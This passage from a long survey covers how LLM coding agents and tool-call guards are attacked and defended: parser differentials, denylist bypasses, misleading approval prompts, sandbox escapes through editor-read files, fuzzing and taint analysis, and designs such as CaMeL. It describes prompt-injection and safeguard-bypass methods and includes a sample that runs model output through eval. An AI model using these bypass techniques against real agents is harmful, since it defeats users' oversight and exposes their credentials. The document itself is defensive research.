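In the airline example, the attack fails whichever reading this parser chooses, because the attacker needed the guard and the executor to read the call differently. If the parser reads I3EHXC, the guard approves the call and the executor cancels the customer's own reservation. If it reads U86B6B, the guard denies the call.

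The guard can easily hand the executor an object when both belong to the same program. If they run on different machines, the call has to travel as text and the executor has to parse it again. The guard should then write the approved call in a canonical form, a single agreed way to write a piece of data. The JSON Canonicalization Scheme is one published standard for this. The form that the researchers recommend leaves no ambiguity for the second parser to resolve, because each name appears once, letters are not written as codes unnecessarily, and it uses only numbers that every component reads the same way.

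The guard also seals the text with a code computed from the call, its ID and a key shared with the executor. The executor checks the seal before it parses anything, and runs the call only under that ID. When the researchers left out the seal, an attacker between the guard and the executor could again insert repeated names, and succeeded on five of the six executors they tried.

The Envoy flaw shows why the guard itself has to write the canonical form. The gateway there also produced unambiguous text, but a different component had done the checking. Kettle describes a similar problem in web servers, where many front ends accept HTTP/2 requests and convert them to HTTP/1.1 for the back end. Kettle considers this more dangerous than using HTTP/1.1 throughout.

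The researchers also generated 7,412 inputs that combined changes to names, values and numbers. None ran the attacker's action when the shared parse was used, though most would have failed without it. When the guard kept the first copy of a repeated name and Python's parser was the executor, 361 inputs succeeded without a defence. Schema validation reduced that to 352, forwarding the original text after a check did not change it, and the shared parse reduced it to zero. The shared parse also worked with Go's decoder, the older segmentio decoder and two official MCP SDKs as executors, and it blocked none of 1,120 ordinary calls written by commercial models.

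Removing a part of the design let some attacks back in. When the software kept undeclared fields, 48 of the inputs succeeded on the older segmentio decoder. When it did not parse JSON inside strings, all 154 dangerous strings that models had copied in the earlier test got through.

That last protection is hard to deploy today because it requires the schema to mark which strings contain JSON, and no schema in the survey did. An operator would have to read the tools' descriptions and add the marks by hand. The researchers' version also doesn't check types or handle schemas that offer alternative sets of fields. An attacker who obtains the shared key can seal any call, and one who copies a sealed call can resend it within its time limit unless the executor keeps a record of the calls it has run.

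The seal also requires support from the executor, which often belongs to another company. Without that company's help, a business can still change its own guard to forward only declared fields in canonical form. This would have stopped the airline attack as tested, with the attacker's gateway in front of the guard, but not if the gateway had been behind it.

Until the executor takes part, the operator can at least log the call the executor received next to the call the guard approved. In the airline case, the log would contain both I3EHXC and U86B6B. Recording only the decisions is not enough. When Shaw made components drop an argument before asking for a decision, the decision stayed the same in 97 of 217 cases, and only a comparison of the recorded requests revealed the omission.

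## Command filters, approval prompts and sandboxes in coding agents

Coding agents do much of their work by writing shell commands. A tool call that runs a command may have only one argument, so the guard and the executor can easily parse the same value from it, but the shell then interprets that value as a small program. The program normally runs with the developer's permissions, so it can access private keys, cloud credentials and other projects on the machine.

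Makers of coding agents rely on three barriers. A command filter compares each command with lists of allowed and forbidden commands. An approval prompt lets a person accept or reject commands that the filter neither allows nor blocks. A sandbox limits what a command can access when it runs. An attacker who plants instructions in a project's files, or in a web page the agent reads, has to get past whichever of these the product uses.

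### Lists of allowed and forbidden commands

In *One Goal, Many Commands*, Chen and Lin (2026) describe how coding agents usually screen commands. The agent's software first rejects any command that matches a denylist, then runs any that matches an allowlist without asking. Everything else goes to the user for approval or, in some products, to a second model. Chen and Lin cite a 93% user approval rate for these requests and conclude that the denylist has to block most harmful commands. The high approval rate alone doesn't show that people approve carelessly, since most of what a coding agent asks to do is probably harmless.

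A denylist names specific commands, but its author usually wants to prevent a result that many other commands can also produce. One project on GitHub blocked six common commands for displaying files that hold passwords and keys, but its list omitted other standard programs that can display the same files.

Chen and Lin built ShellSieve to test whether denylists block what they seem meant to block. A language model identifies operations that a denylist seems meant to prevent, such as deleting a certain file, and suggests other commands that might perform them. ShellSieve runs each command in a sandbox and counts it as a bypass only if the files show that it had the forbidden effect. Of 1,709 denylists from GitHub, between 69.0% and 98.6% failed to block something they seemed meant to block, depending on which kinds of bypass were counted. Completing a list aimed at specific operations would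 take 217 more commands on average. ShellSieve had to infer each author's aim from the blocked commands, and someone who blocks a command to prevent accidents may not expect to stop a determined attacker.

Chen and Lin also found a gap in Claude Code's auto mode, which has a built-in list of commands that can run arbitrary code. Auto mode sends these commands to a model for review, even if the user's allowlist would permit them. The built-in list omitted a standard text-processing program that can start a shell. Chen and Lin reported the gap to Anthropic but don't mention a fix.

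Allowlists can fail for a similar reason. Cohen, Lisichkin and Fogel (2026) report in *The Week of Sandbox Escapes* that OpenAI's Codex CLI ran a Git command without approval because the command's name suggested that it only displayed changes. Some of Git's options write files or start other programs, so the filter also needed to check the arguments. OpenAI fixed the flaw in version 0.95.0.

### How the shell changes a command after the check

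Even a complete list can fail, because the shell changes a command's text after the filter has searched it, which creates another parser differential. Before running a command, the shell removes quotation marks, replaces variables with their values, and runs any nested commands. In `ls $HOME`, for example, it replaces `$HOME` with the path of the user's home folder, so the final command contains a path that was not in the text the filter searched.

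*GuardFall*, published by the security company Adversa AI on 30 June 2026, tested eleven popular open-source agents for this weakness and related ones, and found ten exploitable in at least one configuration.

| Protection | Agents | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Patterns matched against the raw text | Hermes, opencode, Goose | opencode missed 16 of 16 test commands and Goose missed 22 of 23; Hermes failed on every type |
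| Command split into parts before matching | Cline (optional setting), Roo-Code | Cline missed 2 of 13 and Roo-Code missed 4 of 18 |
| A person's approval, with no filter | Aider, Plandex, Open Interpreter | No protection once automatic execution is on |
| Disposable container | OpenHands, SWE-agent | Host protected, except in a mode that runs commands directly on it |
| Five-step check | Continue | None of 21 test commands ran without permission |

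The figure of ten out of eleven agents combines different problems. Five had a filter that missed some commands, and the other five either had no filter or depended on a container that users can turn off.

For an attack to work, the model must also write the harmful command, and the agent must be set to run it without approval. Claude Sonnet 4.6, since superseded, refused direct requests to delete files but wrote equivalent commands when they looked like routine project work. Servers that test code unattended often run commands automatically, and a malicious project can sometimes turn this setting on through a configuration file. SecurityWeek's *Decades-Old Bash Tricks Expose AI Coding Agents to Supply Chain Attacks* calls the exploit complex because of these conditions. Neither account reports fixes or replies from the agents' maintainers.

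Continue performed better because its check imitates some of the shell's own steps:

1. It splits the command into the parts the shell would use, which removes misleading quotation marks.
2. If the command contains a variable, it asks the user.
3. It checks nested commands separately, and never treats the whole command as safer than its parts.
4. If the command passes text to a program that could run it as code, it asks the user.
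5. It refuses certain destructive commands whatever the user's settings.

The coding agent Continue relies heavily on user approval for security because it does not predict the result of every uncertain command. In a live test, its default mode blocked or requested approval for all 24 commands. When Adversa AI used the command-line version with automatic approval, 18 of the 24 ran or would have run, and only those on the list of forbidden commands were still blocked. Continue's command check misses some nested commands and some ordinary programs that become destructive with certain options. It also requires approval for many harmless commands, which gives users a reason to turn on automatic approval.

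One of Adversa AI's attacks would have worked even against a filter that interpreted commands exactly as the shell does. The instruction to delete the developer's cloud credentials was in the test step of a project's build file. Plandex ran the usual test command, which read the file and deleted the credentials.

### When the prompt names the wrong file

An approval prompt helps only if it describes what will happen. Wiz's *GhostApproval*, published on 8 July 2026, tested six coding agents with a project containing a symbolic link, a folder entry that redirects to a file elsewhere. The link looked like a settings file but led to a file outside the project, such as the list of keys that can log in to the developer's machine. When the agent followed the project's instructions to edit the settings, it changed the outside file.

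Cursor, Claude Code and Google's Antigravity asked for approval in prompts that named only the link, not the real file. Claude Code's model had identified that file in its reasoning, but the software did not include it in the approval prompt. Amazon Q Developer and Windsurf wrote the change first and then offered to undo it, and Augment did not ask for approval.

Amazon, Cursor and Google fixed their products in May and June 2026. Augment and the owner of Windsurf had acknowledged the reports, but Wiz knew of no fix from either when it published. Anthropic rejected the report, although current versions of Claude Code warn about links to sensitive files. Anthropic later said the warning had shipped in version 2.1.32, nine days before Wiz's report. Wiz lists the later version 2.1.42 as affected and does not resolve the conflict.

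The fix is for the agent to follow the link before displaying the prompt, show the real destination, warn if it is outside the project, and write nothing until the user agrees.

Kumar (2026), in *Loopjacking*, found that the approval prompt in OpenClaw version 2026.2.23 showed only part of certain shell commands, and that OpenClaw ran the full command after approval. Version 2026.2.24 rejects requests in which the displayed command differs from the full one.

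### When an approval covers a different action

Kumar also tested whether an action could change after a person had approved an accurate description of it. The tests used a mock payment tool and Agno, a framework for building agents. One account could start tasks but not approve payments. An administrator approved a transfer of 20 units to a known vendor. The first account then continued the task with a transfer of 2,000 units to another recipient, and Agno executed it. Agno checked that the task was no longer waiting for approval, but did not compare the new arguments with the approved ones.

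Kumar reproduced this in seven Agno releases, the last of them 3.0.9. *Approve What, Exactly?* (Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill, 2026) repeated the test on version 3.1.3, the latest it measured, and the attack still worked. LangGraph's server had a similar problem in 12 versions, but only if the operator let someone other than the approver edit a pending task. Operators can deny that permission, but Kumar identifies no fix from the vendor. OpenAI's Agents SDK rejected the changed action.

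Kodathala and colleagues examined ten frameworks and agents. They could measure whether the approved action stayed fixed in eight approval mechanisms. Three kept it fixed, one did so unless an attacker could edit the stored session, and four let it change.

Many coding agents can also save an approval. *From Approval to Abuse* (2026) describes how a user may approve a rule based on the agent's proposed command, after which matching commands run without a prompt. Text that the agent has read can therefore influence how much the rule permits.

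In *Approval Laundering*, Wang (2026) studied what saved approval rules allowed in Claude Code 2.1.197. The tasks were harmless and contained no text meant to mislead the model, but Wang set up each project so that a command already permitted by a saved rule could have an effect not stated in its wording.

| What the rule permitted | What happened without a new prompt | Runs |
|---|---|---|
| Running the project's tests | The test script read a file that the rule did not name | 20 of 20 |
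| Displaying files | Another program with the same name ran and changed a file | 20 of 20 |
| A command, in a simulated earlier session | The agent used the rule in the current session | 20 of 20 |
| Running one script | A subagent, a helper started by the main agent, ran it | 18 of 19 |
| One exact Git commit command | The commit included an extra file | 9 of 20 |
| Opening pages on one website | The agent reached another address through the shell | 0 of 19 |

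In the commit test, a Git hook (a program that Git runs automatically) added every changed file before the commit. In most runs where this did not happen, the model had written a narrower command, which Claude Code blocked because it did not match the rule.

These rates do not show how often approvals go wrong in ordinary use, because Wang built the projects to produce the mismatches and decided what each approval should have covered. Some of those decisions are debatable. Someone who chooses "always allow" may well expect the rule to apply tomorrow, and running a project's tests means running whatever its test script contains. The replaced program is harder to excuse, because a rule for displaying files should not let the agent change one. The paper describes no resulting change to Claude Code.

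### Binding an approval to one action

European payment rules address part of this problem. When a customer approves an online payment, the approval code must depend on the amount and the recipient, so it becomes invalid if either changes. Kodathala and colleagues applied the same idea to agents in a system called ASU.

The agent sends its tool call to a gateway on a separate machine. The gateway converts the call to a canonical form, Δ, and computes a digest *h* = SHA-256(Δ), a short code that in practice changes whenever Δ does. It stores the call and displays a description of it on the user's phone. The gateway writes this description from the call itself and puts any explanation from the agent in a box marked as untrusted. If the user approves, the phone signs a message that includes *h*, and the gateway executes the stored call once. If the agent submits different arguments after approval,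 their digest does not match *h* and the gateway refuses them.

Kodathala and colleagues asked 15 language models to approve or refuse an agent's actions. In one test, a user asked the agent to email a report to a manager, and the agent secretly added another recipient. All 15 models approved the email when they read the agent's description of it, and all 15 refused it when they read the gateway's. Across all the attacks tested, using the gateway's descriptions raised the share that the models caught from 30% to 98%. The models also refused 16% of harmless requests that resembled attacks, mostly because of placeholder text in the test material.

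These tests involved no human participants, so they do not measure how carefully a tired developer would read the screen. An agent can also send many requests, hoping the user eventually approves one. ASU limits the number of requests, but this attack still succeeded 45% to 60% of the time against a simulated human approver. Asking for approval on a phone had no measurable benefit over a trustworthy prompt on the agent's own machine, a useful result for developers who cannot require a second device.

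Binding the approval to the command does not control what the command triggers. Wang tested a similar defence that tied approvals to details such as the session and the agent's identity. It stopped the subagent and the reuse from an earlier session, but blocked only one of the nine unwanted commits. In the other eight, the agent ran exactly the command the rule permitted. According to *When the Approved File Is Unchanged* (2026), fixes in released products are even narrower. One ties the approval to a single script, and another prompts the user again when a trusted entry changes.

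*Shall We Approve?* (2026) proposes showing the approver, here a language model, what a command did. The system records the command's effects, including anything the command set up to run at a later build or startup. If the approver agrees, the system keeps the result; otherwise, it gives the agent a reason and asks for a safer alternative. The approver's instructions include a warning that a command may be unsafe even if the record shows no network traffic or use of credentials.

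### Files that take effect outside the sandbox

A coding agent's sandbox usually lets the agent change files in the project folder but protects the rest of the machine. The developer's editor and other tools run outside the sandbox and read the same folder, where some files specify which programs those tools start. An agent can therefore write such a file without breaking the sandbox's limits and cause a program to run outside the sandbox later.

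Cohen and colleagues at the security company Pillar reported seven sandbox and filter failures on 20 July 2026. Four worked this way. In one, the agent changed the copy of Python inside a project. Cursor's Python extension looked for available versions of Python, found the altered copy and ran it with the developer's full permissions. The user might have seen the agent edit a file, but no prompt appeared when the extension ran the altered copy.

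| Product | What happened outside the sandbox | Status |
|---|---|---|
| Cursor | The Python extension ran an altered copy of Python | Fixed |
| Cursor | The Git extension started a program named in Git settings that the agent had written | Fixed in 3.0.0 |
| Cursor | Cursor ran a command from a hook file in the project | Fixed in 3.0.0 |
| Antigravity | The editor ran a task from the project's settings | Downgraded by Google; no fix reported |
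| Antigravity | The agent used macOS features that the sandbox had not blocked | Downgraded by Google; no fix reported |
| Codex, Cursor, Gemini CLI | Docker, a service for running containers, carried out the agent's requests | Fixed |

The Codex allowlist flaw described above is the seventh finding. The Docker flaw did not require a delayed effect. Docker runs outside the sandbox with wide access to the machine, so an agent that can send requests to Docker can use it to do things the agent cannot do directly.

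A sandbox can block changes to files that start programs, but its developers must know which files those are. Cursor protected Git's settings only in their usual location, and the researchers bypassed this by storing them elsewhere, which Git allows. Cohen and colleagues recommend running the helper programs under the same restrictions as the agent, which protects the machine even if the list of sensitive files is incomplete. They also recommend asking the user before the agent creates or changes anything that runs automatically. This will interrupt some legitimate work, because developers often use agents to set up builds and tests.

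### What users have agreed to

Vendors who decline such reports often argue that the user accepted the risk. Anthropic told Wiz that developers must confirm they trust a folder before using Claude Code there. The developer in Wiz's test had also approved the edit, so Anthropic placed the attack outside its threat model, the set of attacks it expects the product to withstand. Google downgraded the Antigravity findings as difficult to exploit, since the attacker would have to trick the user or get them to trust a project with planted instructions.

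This argument is somewhat persuasive, because a developer who builds a downloaded project runs its code with or without an agent. Someone who turns off a container after reading the documentation has also made a choice, but users make no such choice when a project silently turns on automatic execution.

The argument is much weaker when the product has given the user wrong information. Wiz replies that consent requires an accurate prompt, and that agreeing to edit a settings file is not consent to let a stranger log in. Trusting a folder is also little evidence that the developer would approve what the agent adds to it later. If a web page leads the agent to write a new startup task, the developer had no chance to judge that task when deciding to trust the folder.

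Vendors also encourage users to rely on these barriers. Nous Research's Hermes documentation, *Security*, describes command approval and container isolation as security boundaries. Adversa AI argues that a filter makes people confident enough to stop checking commands themselves, but gives no data on how often this happens. Users may also lack a good alternative. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026) describes a review of 290 public misuse reports across 13 agent frameworks, which found that users often had to choose between unrestricted file access and constant approval requests.

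A vendor can reasonably leave a risk to the user if it accurately describes what the barrier is for. For example, SWE-agent blocks some interactive programs because they would make the agent hang. According to Adversa AI, SWE-agent's documentation gives that reason and does not present the blocklist as a security measure.

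## How these flaws are found and how common they are

Researchers found EchoLeak by studying one product closely, which is too slow for checking thousands of programs. Taint analysis and fuzzing, two older methods from software security, are faster. Taint analysis examines a program's code without running it, and fuzzing runs the program on many automatically generated inputs. Both need changes when the program contains a language model.

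### Following model output through a program

Taint analysis looks for a path from a source, where untrusted data enters a program, to a sink. The tool marks the data as tainted at the source and copies the mark to every value computed from it. If a tainted value reaches a sink without passing a suitable check, the tool reports the path.

Suppose a website has a model turn visitors' questions into formulas:

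```
question = request.args["q"]
prompt = "Write this as a formula: " + question
formula = model.generate(prompt)
total = eval(formula)
show(total)
```

The model's answer enters the program in line 3, so the tool marks `formula` as tainted. Line 4 passes it to `eval`, which runs text as code, so the tool reports the path from line 3 to line 4. The developer can fix the flaw by replacing `eval` with a parser that accepts only numbers and arithmetic. The tool must then treat that parser as a valid check, or it will keep reporting the path.

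A tool that traces data from the visitor's question in line 1 has trouble at line 3. It can analyze an ordinary function's code to see how the output depends on the input, but a model has no such code. Xu, Cheng and colleagues (2026) report in *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary* that two widely used checkers, CodeQL and Semgrep, stop tracking the data here because they do not treat a model's answer as a source.

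Marking every model answer as tainted causes false alarms. For example, a model that rates a product review from 1 to 5 returns a single digit, which cannot contain a command, although it may still determine what the program does next. Xu and colleagues' tool, PRISM, therefore sorts how a model handles each piece of inserted text into 25 categories, from copying it word for word to ignoring it. Its F1 score was 81.7%, compared with 47.5% for marking every answer as tainted. PRISM also flagged six known flaws in the agent OpenClaw and raised no alarm on the patched versions.

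PRISM's categories come from prompts that the researchers filled with plausible, ordinary values. A model may ignore ordinary text but follow instructions that an attacker puts in the same place, so a path that PRISM clears could still be dangerous.

Some checkers examine only the model's input. Psalm's *TaintedLlmPrompt* describes a warning for PHP programs that pass user input into a prompt. Nearly every chatbot does this by design, so a developer cannot tell from the warning alone whether the model's answer can do harm.

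### LLMSmith's call chains

*Demystifying RCE Vulnerabilities in LLM-Integrated Apps* (Liu, Deng and colleagues, 2023) introduced LLMSmith, one of the first tools for finding these flaws. LLMSmith starts from functions that execute code and works backwards through their callers until it reaches a function that application developers use. It found 51 such call chains in 11 frameworks for building applications. Seven of them (13.7%) were false alarms that could not be used to run arbitrary code. The researchers counted 20 vulnerabilities in total, and the frameworks' developers confirmed 17.

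They then tested 51 applications (the match with the number of call chains is a coincidence) and successfully attacked 17. Sixteen let them run code on the server, and one let them manipulate database queries. *A Survey on Large Language Model (LLM) Security and Privacy* (2023) cites an earlier version of the work, which lists 13 vulnerabilities in six kits. The 2024 version covers more kits, but the result for applications is still 17 of 51.

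The finding that a third of the tested applications were vulnerable does not generalize to all such applications, because of how the researchers chose their sample. They found 24 of the 51 by searching GitHub for programs that used functions they already knew to be unsafe, and most of the others by searching app markets for similar descriptions. Many of the failed attacks are also weak evidence of security. Of the 34 applications that resisted, 13 malfunctioned and 10 could not run code at all. Of the 20 that seemed able to run code, 16 let the researchers run their own on the server. A few applications avoided the problem by running generated code in the visitor's browser, which is slower to load and supports fewer libraries.

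### Searching for a request that triggers the flaw

A call chain shows that model output can reach a sink, but not that an attacker can get the model to write harmful output. Fuzzing directly tests whether an attacker can. Traditional fuzzers change inputs at random, such as by flipping bits, but random changes to an English sentence seldom make an agent choose a different tool.

Liu, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *Make Agent Defeat Agent*, adapted the method in a tool called AgentFuzz:

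1. AgentFuzz finds the sinks in an agent's code and traces the function calls that lead to each one.
2. A model reads the names of those functions and writes a request that should make the agent use them. If one is called `calculator`, for example, the request asks for a calculation.
3. AgentFuzz sends the request to the agent, records which functions run and gives the request a score.
4. It selects the request with the highest score and changes either the task or the data in it. If a condition in the code blocked the last attempt, AgentFuzz calculates a value that would satisfy the condition.
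5. When a request reaches the sink, AgentFuzz inserts a harmless test value and reports a flaw only if that value arrives.

AgentFuzz scores each request as *F* = 0.5*S* + 0.5*D* − *P*. A model assigns *S*, from 0 to 10, according to how well the functions that ran match the intended ones. *D* is 1 divided by the number of steps left to the sink, and *P* is a penalty for requests that AgentFuzz has already selected often. A new request with *S* = 8 and *P* = 0 that stops two steps short of the sink scores 4 + 0.25 = 4.25.

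Since *D* is at most 1, distance in the code adds no more than 0.5 to the score, while the model's judgement, *S*, can add up to 5. The model's judgement therefore affects the score far more, and the test results fit this. AgentFuzz found 26 flaws when it selected requests at random, 27 when it used distance without the model's judgement, and 34 with the full score.

Those 34 flaws were in 14 of 20 popular open-source agents, which contained 828 calls to sinks. None was a false alarm, because AgentFuzz reported a flaw only after detecting its test value at the sink. It needed about two hours of computing time per flaw and at most $6.90 in model fees per agent. A model might pass on a harmless value but refuse a malicious one, so Liu, Zhang and colleagues also tried real attack code, and all 34 flaws were exploitable. In 14 cases they first had to get past the model's refusals or the developer's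 instructions. Many developers had relied on such instructions even where ordinary code could have checked the value.

On the same 20 agents, LLMSmith found 10 of these flaws and raised 332 false alarms. In some of the false alarms, users had no control over the value that reached the sink. In others, LLMSmith had linked unrelated functions because it matches calls by name. Agents are especially hard to trace this way because they often look up a tool while running, using a name the model has just written. LLMSmith also missed 25 flaws, 16 of them because it recognised only three dangerous functions.

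AgentFuzz misses flaws too. Liu, Zhang and colleagues manually checked 83 of the calls it had not flagged and found one real flaw, in which the agent stored text during one exchange and ran it during the next. At that rate, the unflagged calls would contain about ten flaws, and AgentFuzz would have found nearly 80% of all the flaws. The paper reports that it found 97%, but that figure counts only the 35 flaws the researchers knew about. Both figures are weakly supported because they depend on a single missed flaw.

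*ChainFuzzer* (2026) is a fuzzer that targets flaws involving several tools in one workflow. The fuzzer in *Autonomy Comes with Costs* searches for flaws that let a request use up an agent's computing resources, and found 36 of them in 16 of 20 open-source agents.

### Scanning thousands of projects

Fuzzing requires a working copy of each program, which makes it hard to apply to thousands of projects. *TaintP2X* (He, Wang and colleagues, presented in April 2026) returned to taint analysis, with the model's answer as the source. The tool recognises 97 common interfaces for calling a model. It uses a language model to identify other interfaces that developers wrote themselves, and to discard paths where the prompt is fixed or an existing check looks adequate. Discarding these paths reduces false alarms, but a wrong judgement here could hide a real flaw.

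TaintP2X scanned 4,772 GitHub projects and reported 101 paths in 75 of them, and 74 of the paths led to the execution of code or commands. Developers have confirmed seven vulnerabilities and fixed five. The unconfirmed reports could be false alarms, or the developers may not have answered.

| Tool and test | Programs tested | Flaws confirmed | False alarms |
|---|---|---|---|
| LLMSmith, original test | 11 kits | 20, of which developers confirmed 17 | 7 of 51 call chains |
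| LLMSmith, AgentFuzz researchers' test | 20 agents | 10 | 332 |
| AgentFuzz | 20 agents | 34 | 0 |
| TaintP2X | 4,772 projects | 7, by developers | Unknown; most of the 101 paths are unconfirmed |

He and colleagues also compared the three tools on 35 known vulnerabilities. TaintP2X found 27, LLMSmith 17 and AgentFuzz 7. AgentFuzz did much worse than in its own test, partly because it could not automatically set up and run many of the programs. A developer who already has the program running would not have this problem, so fuzzing is better suited to testing one's own product than to surveying other people's.

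### How often a flaw depends on the model

Vulnerability databases contain many entries for AI software, but attackers can exploit most of these flaws without going through a model. Ma and colleagues collected 2,888 vulnerabilities in 230 open-source components, some of which were general computing libraries. Five researchers reviewed the records and classified 116 as related to language model software. Of these, 41 are the flaws mentioned earlier that an attacker can exploit only through a model. The other 75 were conventional flaws, such as a program that runs hidden code when it loads a model file. In another collection of 1,229 vulnerabilities in language model software, Ma and colleagues found only 11 that an attacker had to exploit through the model.

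Of the 41 flaws, 21 are rated "critical", the highest severity. This is unsurprising, since nearly half of the 41 involve applications that run generated code. Another seven involve generated queries, and seven more involve an agent's choice of tools or arguments.

*LLM-Enabled Open-Source Systems in the Wild* (Shifat, Baburaj and colleagues, 2026) examined security advisories that GitHub published between January 2025 and January 2026. A keyword search returned 295, of which 260 concerned software that runs language models or often supports them. The researchers randomly sampled 100 of the 260 and assigned each to one or more of OWASP's 2025 categories. Twelve involved improper output handling, 20 involved excessive agency, and eight of these involved both. If the sample is typical, about 30 of the 260 advisories involved improper output handling.

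Shifat and colleagues found no new kinds of programming error. The most common errors were familiar ones, such as code injection and command injection, so developers can fix many of them with existing methods. About a fifth of the advisories listed no fix when the researchers collected the data.

### Whether models can repair the flaws

Ma and colleagues also tested how well language models repair these vulnerabilities. They combined five repair tools with four models, including GPT-5.2-Codex and DeepSeek-V4-Pro. A repair counted as successful only if it blocked every test attack and kept the program's normal functions working. The tests replayed fixed malicious outputs instead of calling a live model, so they measured whether the surrounding software was safe once a model had been misled.

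On average, the 20 combinations repaired 25.8% of the 41 flaws that depend on a model, about 11 percentage points less than their average for the 75 conventional flaws. The best combination repaired 22 of the 41. Newer models may do better, but the failures show a mistake that human developers also make.

In one case, a model-written database query could create files on the server. The repair tool's fix blocked a list of dangerous words, including "attach", so it also rejected harmless queries that used "attach" as a name. The developers of the affected kit, LlamaIndex, instead made the database block the dangerous operation. In another case, the chat program ChuanhuChatGPT displayed model-written HTML without sanitising it. The repair tool's fix encoded the HTML in the usual message-processing code but missed messages that took another route. The developers fixed the flaw by turning the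 sanitiser back on at the final display step, which every message passes through.

### Why the counts are hard to compare

These studies count different things, so their totals cannot be meaningfully added together. LLMSmith's 20 vulnerabilities include three LangChain functions that share one entry in the public vulnerability register, so a study that counted entries would report fewer. Three of the 20 can be triggered by loading a file or sending a direct request, so they probably would not count as model-dependent under Ma and colleagues' definition. TaintP2X counts paths through the code, and several paths may belong to one flaw.

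All of the samples also favour open-source software, because researchers can read and run it. EchoLeak was in a service that Microsoft runs on its own servers, so a search of public code or package advisories would not have found it. Even among open-source projects, researchers look more closely at popular ones and those that offer rewards for reports. A project with many advisories may have worse code than its competitors, or just more people checking it. For the same reason, a rise in reports after a new scanning tool appears does not show that software has become less safe.

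### Reported flaws and real attacks

A vulnerability report shows that an attack is possible, not that a criminal has carried one out. The LLMSmith and AgentFuzz researchers made the attacks themselves and reported the flaws to developers. Shifat and colleagues and Ma and colleagues worked from vulnerability records, which describe how a flaw works and how much damage it could do. None of this measures how often attackers use such flaws. Severity ratings don't either, since a flaw can be rated critical before anyone has exploited it.

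Outside researchers also demonstrated the leaks from Microsoft 365 Copilot, ChatGPT and Claude's web tool, and Microsoft said EchoLeak had affected no customers. Prompt injection tops OWASP's 2026 list because of the community vote, not the number of recorded incidents.

Successful attacks may be rare, or victims may not notice them because a leak through an invisible image or a misread tool call can look like normal operation.

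## Designs that limit the damage when the model is misled

A company can limit the harm from flaws it hasn't found and attacks it doesn't notice by assuming that an attacker will sometimes control what the model writes, and restricting what the surrounding software does with that output. One reason to assume this is the poor record of defences that try to make the model recognise or resist planted instructions. Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026), in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, recount a study in which attackers who adapted to each of twelve such defences succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them.

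### Least privilege

Least privilege means giving each task only the data and tools it needs. The office assistant has to open one shared document, summarise it and email the summary to Dana Ortiz. If it can also search the whole mailbox and write to anyone, text planted in the document could make it find a confidential email and send it to a stranger. That leak requires permission to open the document, search the mailbox and write to anyone, so removing any one of these permissions prevents it.

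| Permission removed for this task | What planted text can still do |
|---|---|
| Searching the mailbox and other files | Send a stranger the summary and anything private already in the conversation |
| Choosing the recipient (the wrapper fills in Dana's address) | Put false or private text in an email that only Dana receives |
| Opening documents from outside the company | Nothing, but the assistant can no longer do the task |

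Allowing the email to go only to Dana doesn't restrict the user, because the request already names Dana. This blocks only leaks by email, so the product still needs a browser policy to stop data from leaking through images in the answer.

An assistant that accepts any request needs different permissions for each one. Progent, a guard for tool calls, has a model write rules for each task based on the user's request. Ordinary code then enforces those rules. Its developers tested it on AgentDojo, a public benchmark with 97 everyday tasks and 35 attacker goals in simulated office, Slack, banking and travel accounts. Progent reduced the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0%.

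Narisetty and colleagues repeated the test with a small open model, and the rate fell from 25.8% to 4.2%. An attack they wrote specifically for Progent did no better, at 2.6%, but they tried only one template. Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) found in *AgentDyn* that Progent completed far fewer tasks when there were more tools to write rules for.

### Separating the plan from the reading

Attackers can still use planted text to misuse the tools a task needs. Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed splitting the work between two models. A privileged model receives the user's request and plans the tool calls, but never reads outside text. A quarantined model reads the outside text but has no tools. The privileged model refers to the text by a name such as `$summary-1`, and ordinary software fills in the text later.

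This stops a document from adding steps to the plan, but the document can still change the values that the plan uses. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains this flaw, which researchers at Google DeepMind found. Suppose a user asks the assistant to send Bob a file, and Bob's address is in the meeting notes. The quarantined model has to extract the address, so an attacker who can edit the notes can replace it with their own. The assistant then sends the file to the attacker, even though it follows the plan exactly.

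### Labels that follow the data

Information-flow control deals with this problem by labeling each value. An integrity label records whether the value came from a trusted source, and a confidentiality label records who may read it. When software combines values, the result gets the strictest combination of their labels. A policy then determines which tools may receive the result.

Microsoft's *Information-flow control* gives an example with no attacker. Alex asks an agent to answer some emails. Priya has sent Alex a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who is not allowed to see it yet, has asked about the figures. Only Alex and Priya may read the first email, and only Alex and Marco the second. A reply based on both may go only to people on both lists:

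{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}.

The agent therefore cannot send the reply to Marco without asking Alex. If Priya had copied Marco, the result would be {Alex, Marco} and the agent could send the reply automatically.

Integrity labels spread as in taint analysis, so an address that a model extracts from a stranger's document is labeled untrusted even if it looks normal.

### CaMeL on one email task

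CaMeL, which Google DeepMind's researchers published in 2025, combines the two models with these labels. Suppose the user asks the office assistant to email Dana a summary of the shared document, and says that her address is at the end of it. The privileged model might write this program:

```
doc = open_document("Shared plan")
summary = ask_reader("Summarise this document.", doc)
address = ask_reader("Find Dana Ortiz's email address.", doc)
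send_email(recipient=address, body=summary)
```

CaMeL handles the request in five steps.

1. The privileged model writes the program from the user's request and the tool descriptions, before anything opens the document.
2. An interpreter, which runs the program line by line in a restricted form of Python, opens the document and labels its text as untrusted.
3. The quarantined model, here `ask_reader`, returns a summary and an address. The interpreter labels both as untrusted because they came from the document.
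4. Before sending the email, the interpreter checks its policy. The policy might require a trusted recipient who is allowed to read everything the summary draws on.
5. If the address is already among the user's trusted contacts, the email goes out. Otherwise, the interpreter blocks it or asks the user.

If the document tells the assistant to forward the mailbox, nothing happens, because the program has no such step and the quarantined model has no tools. If the document gives a false address for Dana, the policy catches it in step 5. The user could avoid the question by typing Dana's address into the request, which would make the address trusted.

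Willison points out a benefit for privacy. Reading is easier than planning, so a small model on the user's own computer could read the document, and the company that hosts the privileged model would never receive it.

According to Narisetty and colleagues, CaMeL completed 77% of AgentDojo's tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. CaMeL used about 2.8 times as many tokens. No attack succeeded within the threat model its designers had set.

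### When a fixed plan is not enough

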